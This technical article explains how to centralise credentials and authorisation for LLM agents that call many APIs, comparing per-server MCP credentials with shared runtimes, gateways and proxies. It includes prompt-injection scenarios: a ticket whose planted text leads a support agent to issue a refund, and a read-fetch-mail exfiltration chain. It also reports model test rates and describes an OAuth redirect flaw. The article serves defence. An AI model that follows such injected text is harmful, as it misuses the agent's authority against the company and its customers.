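# Centralised credentials and authorisation for LLM agents that call many APIs through one runtime

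## How agents call APIs and where permission is decided

An LLM agent is software in which a large language model (LLM) chooses actions and ordinary code carries them out. Many of those actions are calls to APIs, the interfaces through which one program gets another to return a record, send a message or move money. Most APIs that handle private data or money require a credential, a secret or signed token that identifies the caller. An agent that works across many APIs therefore needs many credentials. Software between the model and the outside service also has to decide which of the model's requests go through.

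LLM agents commonly call APIs in one of two ways. In the first, each API has its own tool server, a small program that stores the credential for that API and applies its own access rules. In the second, one shared runtime holds all the credentials, receives all of the agent's calls, decides whether to allow each one, and sends those it allows to the APIs.

Suppose a company has a support agent that works through a queue of customer tickets. The agent has four operations, each of which is one action that an API offers. The downstream API is the outside service that carries out the operation.

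| Operation | Downstream API | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| Read ticket | Helpdesk | Brings text written by outsiders into the model's input |
| Look up charge | Payments | Returns a customer's payment record |
| Issue refund | Payments | Moves money out of the company's account |
| Send mail | Mail | Sends any text to any address |

This is an ordinary set of powers. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026), a security audit of agent software, starts from much the same case, a support agent that reads email and refunds payments. The combination is risky because anyone who can open a ticket can send text to a model that can also issue refunds.

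### From the model's request to the HTTP request

A language model only produces output, so other software has to act on it. The developer supplies a list of tools, each with a name, a description and a schema for its arguments. The model can then emit a structured request, known as a tool call, that names a tool and fills in the arguments. The program around the model executes the call and feeds back the result, which can shape what the model does next (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026, *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, a review of 89 sources).

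The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is the common standard for these exchanges. Its main software kits now see close to half a billion downloads a month, according to the July release post by Model Context Protocol (2026). The protocol has three parts, which the Model Context Protocol's *Architecture overview* calls host, client and server. The host is the AI application. A server is a program that offers tools. For each server the host creates one client, which holds the connection. The client sends a `tools/list` request to learn what a server offers and a `tools/call` request to use it. In the format that the Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) lays down, with some metadata left out, a charge look-up would be:

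```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "look_up_charge",
    "arguments": { "charge_id": "ch_4821" }
  }
}
```

The message contains no key for the payments service and not even its address. The tool server supplies both when it turns the message into a web request, which for a typical payments API might look like this:

```http
GET /v1/charges/ch_4821 HTTP/1.1
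Host: api.payments.example
Authorization: Bearer <secret key>
```

The last line is the credential. The model does not need it, and keeping it out of the model's input is safer because anything in the input can appear in the output.

Software or a person can stop the call at several points along this path. The server can leave a tool out of its list, because the Model Context Protocol lets the list vary with the caller's permissions. The host can ask a human to confirm the call, and the specification recommends that someone always be able to deny it. A gateway, a shared runtime in front of existing tool servers, can refuse to forward the call. Since the July 2026 version of the protocol, it can do so without reading the message body, because the tool's name is in an HTTP header. The server can refuse the call before adding the credential, and the downstream API can reject the request.

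These places differ in the information available to them. A gateway that reads only the tool's name cannot distinguish a refund of €5 from one of €5,000. The payments API receives the amount and the key, but usually not the ticket or employee behind the request. The company's own code can last refuse a call just before the credential is attached, when it can have both the arguments and the caller's identity. This makes that step the natural enforcement point, where the system stops a call or lets it through. Surapani and colleagues centre their review on this step because they hold that identity, intent, permission and policy must all come together there.

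### Keys, tokens and what they establish

The simplest credential is an API key, a fixed string that a service gives its customer. Whoever holds the key can use it until someone revokes it. Some services take a username and password instead. Others use OAuth, a standard that lets a program obtain an access token, usually temporary, without needing the user's password.

OAuth has four roles. The resource owner, often a user, has something to protect. The client is the program that needs access. The authorization server gets the user's consent where necessary and issues a token, and the resource server accepts the token and carries out the request. A token comes with scopes, which are named permissions such as `files:read`, and it can have an audience, which is the server the issuer meant it for. Under the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) rules, an MCP server is the resource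 server. The client must send its token with every HTTP request, and the server must reject any token meant for another audience. These rules are optional in MCP, however. Local servers, which run on the same machine as the host and exchange messages with it directly, are supposed to take their credentials from their environment instead.

A nightly job that reconciles charges runs without a user, so it uses a service account, which is an identity that belongs to software. It can get its own token through OAuth's client credentials flow. The support agent could also run this way, or it could carry a delegated token, which lets it act for a named employee and records both identities.

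A call usually involves two credentials. The caller presents one to the tool server or runtime, which presents another to the payments API. The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* forbids servers from accepting a token meant for another service and passing it on, partly because the downstream logs may then show the wrong source for the request.

When a server refuses a call on permission grounds, it returns 401 if the token is missing or invalid, and 403 if the token is valid but does not cover the operation. These codes follow the distinction between authentication and authorisation. In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), Saltzer and Schroeder defined authenticating as verifying the identity of whoever makes a request, and authorising as granting a principal access. A principal, in their usage, is the entity that holds permissions and is therefore the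 unit of accountability.

A system can authenticate a request correctly and still authorise it wrongly. A valid payments key shows that a request comes from the company, but not that this refund, on this ticket, should happen. Scopes limit what a key can do, but often coarsely, since a scope that covers refunds may cover all of them. Mellafe Zuvic examined the public code of the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to the payments company Stripe, and found that it had a list of permitted actions and relied on restricted keys, but within those limits forwarded whatever amount and customer the model supplied.

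### One server per API, and the shared runtime

MCP usually uses one server per API. *DADL* (Dunkel, 2026), which proposes describing APIs in plain configuration files, cites an analysis of 116 official MCP servers. In that analysis, 88.6% of the servers wrapped ordinary web APIs in whole or in part, and 92% of the tools did little except pass calls along. Here, the support agent connects to three servers, one each for helpdesk, payments and mail. Each server stores its own credential and applies its own permission rules.

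A shared runtime replaces the three with one. In Dunkel's version, every API has a description file that refers to its credential by a logical name such as `vault/stripe-secret-key`, and the runtime looks up the real secret only when it makes a request. The file can also give each operation an access level, which labels how much harm the operation can do. A company that already has tool servers can put a gateway in front of them to get one enforcement point without rewriting them, although the old servers may still hold their own keys.

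Two principles from Saltzer and Schroeder's paper, summarised in the lecture slides *Design Principles for Security-conscious Systems*, explain the appeal of a single checkpoint. Least privilege means running with the smallest set of powers the job requires, so an agent that only answers billing questions should have no refund operation. Complete mediation means checking authority on every access to every object. Checking only at login or when a developer picks the agent's tools does not meet that standard.

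Mellafe Zuvic distinguishes between which tools an agent has and whether a particular call, with its actual arguments, may proceed. The audit covered the public code of the Stripe toolkit and two widely used agent frameworks, LangChain/LangGraph and LlamaIndex. All three restrict the list of tools, but by default none has a mandatory check on the argument values before a call runs, so developers have to add one themselves.

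Another principle on the same 1975 list, "least common mechanism", is an argument against centralising credentials. It is the principle that designers should minimise the subsystems that many parts share or rely on, and a runtime that holds every key is such a subsystem. Centralising the keys makes complete mediation easier to achieve, but it also makes a break-in more damaging.

### The confused deputy

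*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) gives the standard reason for checking every call, even when the agent is the company's own and its credentials are in order. It describes an incident involving a compiler about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time.

The compiler was stored in a directory called SYSX. Users could run it and name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also collected usage statistics in (SYSX)STAT, so Tymshare gave it a licence to write files in its home directory. That directory also held the billing records, in (SYSX)BILL. One user learnt that name and supplied it as the debugging file. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which opened the file because the compiler had the licence. The debugging output overwrote the billing records.

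The obvious patches do not work well. Blocking the compiler from writing debugging output into SYSX also blocks users who have a legitimate reason to put output there. Blocking only (SYSX)BILL leaves the other sensitive files exposed. Tymshare added a system call that let the compiler specify whose authority it was using, but some applications soon needed more than two authorities, and the rule for opening a file grew to fourteen logical operators. Hardy argued that the compiler ran with "authority stemming from two sources", its user's and its own, and had no way to specify which one to use for a given write. The term "confused deputy" now means a program tricked into using its own authority for someone who lacks it.

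The compiler's licence is an example of ambient authority. A program has ambient authority when it can act on an object just by naming the object and the action, because the system checks which program is running and does not require proof of permission with the request. Hardy's remedy was the capability, which Saltzer and Schroeder define as an unforgeable ticket that proves its holder's right to a particular object. The user would give the compiler a capability for the output file. A user with no right to the billing records would not have a capability for them, and so could not give one to the compiler.

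Most agent tool calls resemble the Tymshare case more than Hardy's remedy. The string `ch_4821` is only a name, which anyone can type into a ticket. The power to refund the charge comes from a key, which the server adds wherever the name came from. Under Model Context Protocol guidance, an identifier that a server with authentication hands out for later use, such as a shopping-basket number, is likewise "a name, not a capability", and the server should check the caller's right to it on every call. A company that calls other firms' APIs mostly has to accept the keys and tokens those firms issue, so it cannot simply switch to capabilities and has to rely on checks instead.

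### Prompt injection as a confused-deputy problem

A customer who has received their goods could open a ticket claiming they never arrived, and add that company procedure requires a full refund of charge `ch_4821` before anyone replies. If the model follows that text, it emits a well-formed `issue_refund` call, the payments server attaches a valid key, and the refund is issued. This is prompt injection, in which an agent follows text in the data it reads as if it were an instruction. It lets the customer use the agent's access to the payments API, which they could not call directly.

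*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) precisely defines the classic confused deputy problem as an agent accessing a resource that it has permission to reach but the authenticated user who set the task does not. In the paper's example, an employee asks an agent with access to the personnel database for everyone's salaries. A runtime that checks each call against the user's own permissions would stop this.

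That comparison would not stop the refund, because the authenticated user in the ticket case is a support employee who may well have the right to issue refunds. The ticket's author lacks that right but never logged in to anything. *Silent Egress* (2026), a study of agents that leak data after reading web pages, distinguishes older cases, where the deputy is confused about whom it serves, from injection, where it is confused about what that person intended. Surapani and colleagues accordingly want the system to have two records when it decides whether to allow a request, one showing who delegated authority to whom and the other showing where the content behind the request came from. The helpdesk belongs in both, as a system the agent has permission to read and as a source of text that nobody should trust.

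Better models reduce the problem but don't remove it. Mellafe Zuvic reports a sandboxed test of 27 models in which the injected text presented a forbidden action as a necessary step in the user's task. The 12 cheaper models attempted the action in 60% of trials on average, and the 15 flagship models in 19%. Individual models ranged from Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview, which never attempted it, to GPT-4o mini, which always did. The test harness blocked these attempts, and newer models may do better, but a 19% rate is still too high to trust a model with decisions such as whether to issue a refund.

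The model's design is another reason not to rely on it. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, from Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), advises treating the model as an "inherently confusable deputy" because the underlying technology does not separate data from instructions. In SQL injection, text typed into a web form runs as a database command, and keeping commands separate from data reliably prevents this. ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks* reports the agency's view that prompt injection may never have as complete a fix. Tymshare could give its compiler a way to declare whose authority it was using, but a declaration from the model would provide little assurance, since the ticket's author may have influenced that too.

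The decision therefore has to be made outside the model. For each tool call, the runtime must decide which credential to use and whether to use it. The credential might be the company's payments key, the agent's service account or a delegated token for the employee on shift. Whether to use it depends on the caller, the operation, the arguments and, ideally, the origin of the text that prompted the call. With the dishonest ticket, the runtime could choose the right credential and still be wrong to send the refund.

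## Choosing between per-server credentials and one shared runtime

Both designs can keep the payments key out of the model's input and block the dishonest refund. They differ mostly in upkeep and in what happens when something goes wrong.

| | Per-server credentials | Shared runtime |
|---|---|---|
| Where secrets sit | With each tool server | In one store that the runtime reads |
| Who decides access | Whoever wrote or configured each server | Whoever writes the central policy |
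| Rotation (replacing a key) | Update every server that holds the key | Update one entry |
| When an employee leaves | Remove access server by server | Remove access once |
| Audit | Combine logs in different formats | Search one log |
| Adding an API | Write or install a server and deploy it | Add a description of the API and review it |
| What one compromise exposes | Usually one API's key | Potentially every key |

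A shared runtime simplifies key rotation and the removal of employees' access less than it may seem. The outside service issues the new key in either design, so a company with 20 keys still has to rotate 20 keys. The runtime only saves it from having to find every copy. Removing a departed employee's access to the runtime is enough if the employee reached the APIs only through it, but someone who copied the payments key to a laptop can keep using it until the company replaces it.

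Separate servers limit the damage from a compromise only if they are isolated from one another. Three local servers running under the same user account on one machine can usually read one another's files, so an intruder on that machine may get all three keys. Separate keys also do little against prompt injection, because the agent can already call all three servers.

### The count for 20 APIs

Suppose the company goes from calling three APIs to calling 20. The count below excludes the key settings, permission rules and logs inside each outside service, because those exist whatever the company does. "Policy engine" here means any code that applies access rules to calls.

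| Design | Credential stores | Policy engines | Logs |
|---|---|---|---|
| 20 servers with their own credentials | 20 | 20 | 20 |
| One shared runtime | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Gateway over 20 servers that keep their keys | 20 | 21 | 21 |
| One proxy that only adds credentials | 1 | None for operations | 1 |
| Hybrid: 17 APIs in the runtime, 3 on their own servers | 4 | 4 | 4 |

The figures for separate servers are upper limits. Twenty servers can fetch their keys from one secrets manager and send their logs to one system, which gives a company much of the benefit of central storage and audit without a shared runtime.

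Access decisions are harder to share between servers. If one server issues refunds and another sends mail, a rule that only employees on shift may do either has to be implemented twice, perhaps by different authors in different programming languages. Dunkel argues that an organisation can review ten tools one at a time but not 1,500, and therefore needs a few rules that cover whole classes of tools.

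Separate servers cannot enforce some rules, because each server receives only its own calls. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (Errico, Ngiam and Sojan, 2025) describes an attack in which the agent reads planted instructions in one system, fetches private data from another and sends it out through a third. The support agent can do this with a ticket, a payment record and an email. The mail server receives what looks like an ordinary request, with no sign that the text came from a payment record or that a ticket prompted it. A shared runtime handles all three calls, so it could enforce a rule that, after looking up a charge, the agent may email only the customer who paid it. The host application also handles all three, but the company would have to build the rule into every agent application it uses.

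### How separate servers handle credentials in practice

For *From REST to MCP*, the analysis of 116 servers that Dunkel cites, Mastouri, Ksontini and colleagues (2025) read the source code of servers in MCP's official catalogue. They began with the 345 servers listed on 31 July 2025 and kept the 116 that had real code, a vendor with a public web API, and at least ten stars on GitHub, a rough sign of use. They classified 114 of these, leaving out two that generated their tools while running. In 87 of the 114, every tool called the vendor's REST API, the usual kind of web API, in which each request combines an HTTP method with an address. Those 87 servers authenticated to the vendor as follows.

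| Credential | Servers | Share |
|---|---|---|
| API key | 42 | 48.3% |
| HTTP bearer token | 15 | 17.2% |
| Several credentials together | 11 | 12.6% |
| OAuth 2.0 | 9 | 10.3% |
| Cloud identity or command-line login | 9 | 10.3% |
| Username and password | 1 | 1.1% |

Of the 87 servers, 80 only wrapped the API, with routine extras such as error handling. Only three added controls such as caching, rate limits or response cleaning, and 64 offered every tool with no setting to turn some off. So in practice, the 20 policy engines counted above often enforce no policy. If a payments server only wraps the API, refunds are limited only by what the key allows.

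Server developers do restrict access more crudely, by leaving operations out. Mastouri and colleagues could compare the tools of 42 servers with the vendor's full API description, and the median server exposed 19% of the operations. On average, servers exposed 38% of the read-only operations and 20% of those that delete something. Leaving out an operation stops agents from calling it through that server, but a support agent that has to issue refunds needs the refund tool.

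This sample shows how developers write well-known public servers. It doesn't cover the servers that companies write for themselves, and source code can't show where a company keeps its key, how often the company rotates it or how broad the key's permissions are.

*What Happens Locally, Leaks Globally* (2026), a study of leaks in MCP server code, describes one real server that writes a request header containing its token to a debug log and another that prints its authentication key to standard output. If 20 servers each hold their own key, any of them could make this kind of mistake, but a shared runtime that logged its headers would put all 20 keys in one file.

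Credentials also collect on the machines where agents run. *Caging the Agents* (Maiti, 2026) reports on nine agents in production at a healthcare technology company. An audit found 12 API keys in one agent's shell start-up file, and every process on another agent's machine could read that agent's file of stored credentials.

### Remote servers and their logins

Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, measured how servers on the public internet check the other credential in a call, the one the caller presents. They searched FOFA and Shodan, which index internet-connected machines, and collected 28,715 candidate addresses. They sent each one MCP's opening message, and 7,973 answered as live MCP servers.

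Of these 7,973 servers, 3,233 (40.55%) let anyone use their tools without a credential, 2,312 (29.00%) accepted a fixed key or token, and 2,428 (30.45%) used OAuth. Most of the open servers the researchers examined were tests or demonstrations. One was a company's customer database, meant for internal use, and any visitor could retrieve more than 5,000 records with names, phone numbers and addresses.

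The researchers then tested 119 OAuth servers in depth. They started with the 1,118 that supported dynamic client registration, which lets a client application register itself with the authorization server without an administrator's approval. They then removed 387 duplicates, 32 servers that turned out to need no authentication, 573 they could not test and 7 with an incomplete login process.

Their tool monitored the traffic as a coding assistant logged in to each server. It reconstructed each login from the first request to the final token, then checked for nine types of flaw. Where monitoring was not enough, it sent altered requests to test whether the server accepted them. Manual checks confirmed 325 of the tool's 379 alerts as flaws and dismissed the other 54. All 119 servers had at least one flaw. The researchers reported the confirmed flaws to the vendors and obtained nine CVE identifiers,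 the public reference numbers for known vulnerabilities.

The most common flaw, found on 114 servers, was that an anonymous client could register any return address. After a user approves a login, the authorization server sends a one-time code to the client's return address, and the client exchanges the code for an access token. An attacker could register their own address and send a victim a genuine login link. If the victim approved the login, the code would go to the attacker, who could exchange it for a token and act as the victim. On a payments server, that could include issuing refunds.

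The finding that all 119 servers had a flaw is weaker than it sounds, because the researchers picked servers that let clients register themselves, and flaws in that feature account for much of the total. The servers they could not test include 316 behind strict enterprise access controls, which may well be better defended. They also didn't test any shared runtime for the same flaws, and a gateway that accepted any return address would expose 20 APIs to the same flaw. The study does show that many separate operators make the same few mistakes, which have to be fixed server by server.

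*Exposed by Design* (2026), a second scan, confirmed 640 MCP servers on the internet and tested 414, of which 91.8% lacked OAuth. In Zhou and colleagues' larger sample, about 70% lacked it, counting both open servers and those with fixed keys. A server without OAuth may still require a key, so neither figure is the share of open servers. The second scan also found a turnover of 41.6% in three days, which the paper presents as a sign of developers experimenting more than of hardened production systems. Internet scans can't reach servers inside a company's network, where a support agent's tools would often be.

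### The case for centralising

*A Gateway Architecture for Enterprise MCP Authentication* (Kumar, Wang and Manoharan, 2026) gives the best description of the problem inside a company, written by a team that had it. It describes how large organisations went from no MCP servers to dozens within a year. Each team could set up a server in an afternoon and chose its own authentication. Some servers had none because they were "internal only", others used one key for all callers, and a few had full OAuth.

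Kumar and his co-authors give three reasons for building a gateway. Authorisation was inconsistent because each server decided on its own who could call it. Audit logs were split across a dozen systems in incompatible formats, so finding out who had used which tool on a given day meant matching them up. Removing a departing employee's access meant contacting every server's team.

In this design, callers log in once to the gateway, which selects the downstream credential for each call. The servers stay, but they only verify tokens issued by the gateway, using a shared library. The gateway controls which tools a caller may reach, and the downstream system controls which records that caller may touch. For the support agent, the gateway would control whether it may use the refund tool, and the payments service would control which accounts its credential covers.

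According to Kumar and colleagues, the OAuth standards were mature, and the hard part was getting every server team to agree to route its traffic through the gateway instead of building its own login. The benefit became clear during a security review, when one query of the gateway's log showed what every agent had done for every user in the past month.

Dunkel's proposal goes further and removes most of the servers. Its description files use DADL, short for Dunkel API Description Language, which is based on YAML, a plain-text configuration format. A shortened file for the payments API, without the definitions of its arguments, might look like this:

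```yaml
backend:
  name: payments
  type: rest
  base_url: https://api.payments.example/v1
  auth:
    type: bearer
    credential: vault/payments-key
  tools:
    look_up_charge:
      method: GET
      path: /charges/{charge_id}
      access: read
      description: "Return one payment record"
```

When the agent asks for `look_up_charge`, the runtime finds this entry, checks the caller against the policy, sends the request with the real key and trims the response before returning it. The file holds only the key's name, so the company can keep the file in an ordinary code repository and review changes to it like any other code change. The `access` line gives one of four standard access levels.

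DADL has a security advantage even without centralisation, because a reviewer can read in the file every HTTP endpoint that its tools can reach. A hand-written server can assemble an address while it runs, so its reviewer has to work out what the code might do. DADL allows small scripts that combine several tools, but they can call only tools that the file defines.

Dunkel also argues that adding an API to the shared runtime takes little work. A public registry held 20 files with 1,833 tools in April 2026, at a median of 13 lines per tool, and Dunkel reports that a new API consistently has its first working tool in under an hour when a language model drafts the file. But separate servers now take little work to write too. Mastouri and colleagues built AutoMCP, which generates a server from an API's published specification. In their tests, 76% of the sampled tools worked at the first attempt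 and 94.2% worked after automatic repairs to the specifications. The company would still have to deploy and maintain each generated server and manage its key, which is the work a shared runtime saves.

Centralising also has a drawback, because an agent connected to everything could have hundreds of tool descriptions in its input. Kumar's team added a search function so that the agent loads only the tools it needs. Dunkel's runtime gives the model one tool for searching and another for running short programs.

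Dunkel acknowledges most of DADL's limits. It can't describe APIs that need custom request signing, persistent connections or a lot of application logic. A DADL file can fall out of date when the vendor changes the API, just as a hand-written server can. The access labels depend on the judgment of the person who assigns them, and the format leaves enforcement to the runtime.

Storing credentials centrally doesn't necessarily make them secure. ToolMesh, an open-source runtime built for DADL files, resolves credentials by name on the server side, but its default store reads them from environment variables, and support for dedicated vaults is only planned. An intruder who could read that process's environment would have all the credentials.

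Both papers are by people who built the systems they describe, and neither includes a controlled security comparison. Dunkel declines to benchmark DADL against MCP servers, arguing that the comparison is operational and depends on which server one picks. Kumar and his co-authors report experience from production but don't count incidents before and after. The savings in audit and offboarding are still believable, because they follow almost directly from having one log and one place to remove access. Neither paper shows whether a company with a shared runtime suffers fewer or smaller breaches.

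### Designs in between

A company that already has 20 working servers would probably start with a gateway. Errico and colleagues, who all work for technology vendors, propose routing all MCP traffic through one. But a gateway controls and logs only the calls that pass through it. If the payments server still accepts direct connections, an agent or an employee can bypass the gateway and use the key that the server holds. To prevent this, the servers have to reject callers without a gateway token, as in Kumar's design, or the network has to block every other route to them.

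A credential-only proxy does less than a shared runtime. It runs outside the agent's environment and adds keys to outgoing web requests. Anthropic's guide *Securely deploying AI agents* recommends this pattern because the key never reaches the agent. The proxy can also log requests and restrict which addresses the agent may contact.

The main practical difficulty is encryption. The agent's software encrypts requests to the payments service before they reach the proxy, so the proxy has to decrypt each request, add a header containing the key and encrypt it again. The agent's machine must therefore trust the proxy's certificate. Some programs also ignore proxy settings and connect directly, so the company has to redirect their traffic at the network level. Anthropic's alternative is a custom tool or MCP server that passes requests to a service outside the agent's environment. This avoids decrypting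 traffic but needs a tool for each service.

In *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026) tested their own company's product of this kind. They ran code inside the agent's sandbox, a restricted environment for running programs, and made 16 checks, all of which came out as they had expected. A request to GitHub succeeded with the vault supplying the credential, and the code found no trace of the credential in environment variables, the usual files or the request as the code had prepared it. Requests to three services that echo back whatever they receive didn't contain the credential either. The researchers did not test redirects, which might carry a credential to another address, or an attack on one of the permitted services.

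One connector failed because someone had configured the vault to put the key in a header instead of in the URL, as the provider required, so the provider refused the request. Nothing leaked, but storing the key centrally did not ensure that the connector worked.

A more serious limit is that the proxy adds the key to bad requests as well as good ones. Kenney and colleagues used their own rough judgement to score eight threats out of 25, based on likelihood and impact, with and without the vault. The vault cut the score for a secret pasted into a prompt from 25 to 4. The score for a connector with too many permissions fell only from 20 to 15, and that for prompt injection in outside content from 25 to 12. They call the vault "necessary rather than sufficient". In the dishonest ticket example, the proxy would keep the payments key safe but still send the refund.

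The proxy doesn't have to be central. Maiti's solution to the scattered keys was a small proxy beside each agent, which held that agent's credentials and limited its destinations, request rate and request size. This keeps secrets away from the agent without putting all of the company's keys in one process, but configuration is again spread across many places.

Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents* describes a hosted agent service that keeps the OAuth tokens for MCP tools in a vault outside the sandbox. The agent sends its tool calls to a proxy along with a session token, and the proxy fetches the matching credential from the vault and calls the outside service. In an earlier version, code that Claude wrote ran in the same container as the credentials, so an injected instruction could expose them just by getting Claude to read its own environment.

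A hybrid keeps some tool servers and moves the other APIs into the runtime. Dunkel expects this to be the realistic arrangement. ToolMesh already supports it by feeding both existing MCP servers and DADL files into the same execution process, according to its *Anatomy of an Enterprise Tool Library*. In the hybrid counted above, the company would maintain four credential stores but could still apply one policy to every call.

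### When separate servers are the better choice

With three APIs and one team, a shared runtime may take more work than it saves. The support agent's company could store three keys in a secrets manager, put a refund limit in the payments server and send three logs to one place. Nobody has measured how many APIs would make this impractical. The number of teams probably matters more, since the problems Kumar describes came from many teams making different choices.

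Some APIs also need code of their own. Amazon's cloud services, for example, have the caller compute a new signature for each request, so adding a fixed key to a header doesn't work. Other APIs keep a connection open and send data both ways, which doesn't fit a configuration format built around single requests and responses. Integrations that are mostly business logic should also be written in code rather than in a configuration file. A shared runtime could include special code for these cases, but that code would need as much care as a separate server and would run alongside everyone else's keys.

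Isolation is the strongest reason to keep a server separate, and it follows Saltzer and Schroeder's advice to minimise shared mechanisms. A key that can move money needs better protection than one that reads tickets, and a flaw in the code that parses helpdesk responses should not expose the payments key. The company could run the payments server on its own machine, with its own key and a hard cap on refunds, and put helpdesk and mail in the shared runtime. Refund requests would still pass through the runtime to be checked against the common policy and recorded in the common log. An attacker who took over the runtime could request refunds from the payments server, but could not read its key or raise the cap.

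## Identifying the caller and attaching the right credential

Suppose a finance manager connects the payments server to the company's account, which lets the server issue refunds. If it never checks who is calling, it will issue them for the support agent, for a script on another team's machine and for an intruder who finds its network address. None of these callers needs the payments key, because the server adds it to every request. Huang, Dai and colleagues (2026) call this failure caller identity confusion in *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile*.

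### How common the failure is

The study covers 6,137 MCP server projects, written in Python, JavaScript or TypeScript and drawn from two existing collections. Its analysis tool first finds the code that runs when a `tools/call` request arrives. It then traces each path from that code to a sensitive operation, such as running a command or calling an outside service, and looks for a check that applies to the current call. Where a check exists but its effect is unclear, the tool runs the server and tests whether a call succeeds using an authorisation that the server already holds.

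It found insecure authorisation in 2,846 servers, or 46.4%. Some never checked callers. Others checked once, for example at start-up, and reused the result for everyone. Still others checked while running, but relied on shared state in memory or covered only some of their tools. Popular projects were no safer. The study classed 48.1% of servers with up to 50 GitHub stars as secure, against 34.8% of those with more than 1,000, although the second group is small.

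One Slack server and one server for Amazon's cloud-cost data logged in at start-up with powerful credentials, then accepted calls from anyone who could reach them. A stranger could read and post Slack messages without stealing a credential, and Slack would receive only a valid token. Huang and colleagues separately examined 87 popular MCP-related projects and found eight with authentication flaws that could let an attacker run commands on the server.

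The 46.4% is the share of projects whose code has the weakness, but an outsider could exploit fewer of them. An attacker needs a way to send calls to the server, and a local server that exchanges messages directly with one host application takes calls only from that application. The tool may also have counted some secure servers as insecure, because in tests it recognised only about nine in ten of the authorisation checks that were present. Limits on who can send calls protect a shared runtime less, because it exists to serve many callers. If it has the same weakness, all of those callers can use every key it holds.

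The runtime therefore has to establish who is calling on every request and choose the credential on that basis.

### Three identity flows

The gateway that Kumar and colleagues run divides callers into people and automated jobs. It handles their calls in one of three ways, depending on whose identity the downstream API receives.

| Flow | What the caller presents | What the gateway checks | What the gateway attaches |
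|---|---|---|---|
| User as themselves | A session handle from the company login | Whether the user's role allows the tool | That user's token |
| Job as a service account | The service account's own token | Whether the service account's role allows the tool | A credential stored in advance |
| User through a service account | A session handle from the company login | Whether this user may act through this service account | The service account's credential |

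An agent can act as the user, for example when an employee asks it to find a message in their own mailbox. The employee logs in through single sign-on (SSO), the login system that the company's applications share. The gateway keeps the resulting token and gives the client a session handle, a string that means nothing outside the gateway. The client sends the handle with each call. The gateway looks up the matching token, refreshes it if it has expired, checks the employee's role and forwards the call. The mail service then applies the employee's own permissions, so the agent can't open a colleague's mailbox.

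The employee's machine receives only the handle, never the real token. A thief who copies the handle may be able to use the gateway as that employee until the handle expires, so it needs the same protection as a token.

The nightly job that reconciles charges has no browser and nobody to approve a login, so it logs in to the SSO with its service account's credentials. It sends the gateway only the token it gets back. The job never has the payments key, which an administrator put in the gateway when the payments server was set up. The gateway checks the job's role and then attaches that key. Kumar's team uses OAuth's password grant for the login, but the draft OAuth 2.1 standard drops that grant, so a new system should use the client credentials flow.

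**User through a service account.** Most refunds would work this way. A payments company typically issues keys to a business, not to each employee, so every refund goes out under the same credential. The gateway identifies the employee from the session and checks that they may act through the payments service account before it attaches the key. Without that check, anyone who could reach the refund tool could do everything the service account can, much as anyone who could run Tymshare's compiler could write to the compiler's home directory. The gateway also records both identities, because the payments API's log will show only the service account.

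The runtime has to check that a request is authorised before it attaches the credential. If the software fails between these two steps, the request goes out without a credential and the API refuses it. If the runtime attached the credential first, the same failure could let an unauthorised refund through.

### Why an automated job must not obtain a user's token

The gateway at first served only people, but teams later asked for nightly digests and other unattended work. If an employee, Maria, logged in once and a reconciliation job reused her token, the job could do whatever the token allowed, perhaps including reading her mail, even when she was away. The logs would attribute its actions to her. When she left the company, either the job would stop working or someone would keep her access active. If the job read a ticket containing planted instructions, the ticket's author could act through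 it with Maria's permissions as well as the job's own.

Kumar and colleagues prevent this by tying each type of login to a type of caller. Only people can use the flow that produces a user's token, because it requires someone to approve access in a browser. Jobs can use client credentials, which never carry a user's identity. The gateway refuses a job's request if it needs a user's identity. A job that needs to read one employee's calendar can use a service account with access to that calendar.

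OAuth doesn't impose this rule. An authorization server can issue a refresh token, which a program exchanges for new access tokens. One accepted use of refresh tokens is to let a program keep working after the user has gone. The company has to configure its SSO and runtime so that jobs can't get them.

### Token exchange

The support agent often resembles both a human caller and an automated job, because an employee starts the work but the agent chooses the calls. A token that names only the employee doesn't identify the agent, and the employee's permissions are lost if the token names only the agent.

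OAuth token exchange, which Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, define as RFC 8693, can put both in one token. It works as follows when Maria uses the support agent:

1. Maria logs in, and the agent application receives a token that identifies her.
2. The agent sends this token to the authorization server as the `subject_token`. It can add an `actor_token` that identifies the agent, and it names the service it wants to call.
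3. The authorization server verifies the agent's own credentials and Maria's token, then decides whether the agent may act for her.
4. If so, it issues a new token for that service.

The contents of the new token, once decoded, might be:

```json
{
  "iss": "https://login.company.example",
  "aud": "https://runtime.company.example",
  "exp": 1796468460,
  "scope": "tickets:read refunds:create",
  "sub": "maria@company.example",
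  "act": {
    "sub": "support-agent"
  }
}
```

The `sub` (subject) field identifies the person whose rights are in use, and the `act` (actor) field identifies the program using them. `iss` is the issuer, `aud` the audience and `exp` the expiry time. The issuer signs the token, so the agent can't change the names. The runtime can then allow a refund only if Maria may issue refunds and the support agent may issue them for her.

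The standard calls this arrangement delegation. It also allows impersonation, in which the new token names only Maria, so the receiving service can't tell the agent from her. Impersonation is easier for older services that don't support `act`, but the service can't use the agent's identity to give it fewer rights than Maria, and the record omits the agent.

Several details of the exchange affect its safety:

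- **Who may ask.** The standard leaves it to each company whether programs must authenticate to exchange a token. If they needn't, anyone who steals Maria's token can trade it for others. A `may_act` field in her token can name the program allowed to act for her.
- **Which audience to check.** Maria's original token is meant for the agent application, so the authorization server has to check for that audience during the exchange. Kumar and colleagues report that checking for the gateway's audience instead is the most common misconfiguration.
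- **How long the result lasts.** The exchange doesn't link the two tokens. Revoking Maria's original token doesn't necessarily revoke the new one, which is a reason to keep the new one short-lived. An example in the standard lasts one minute.

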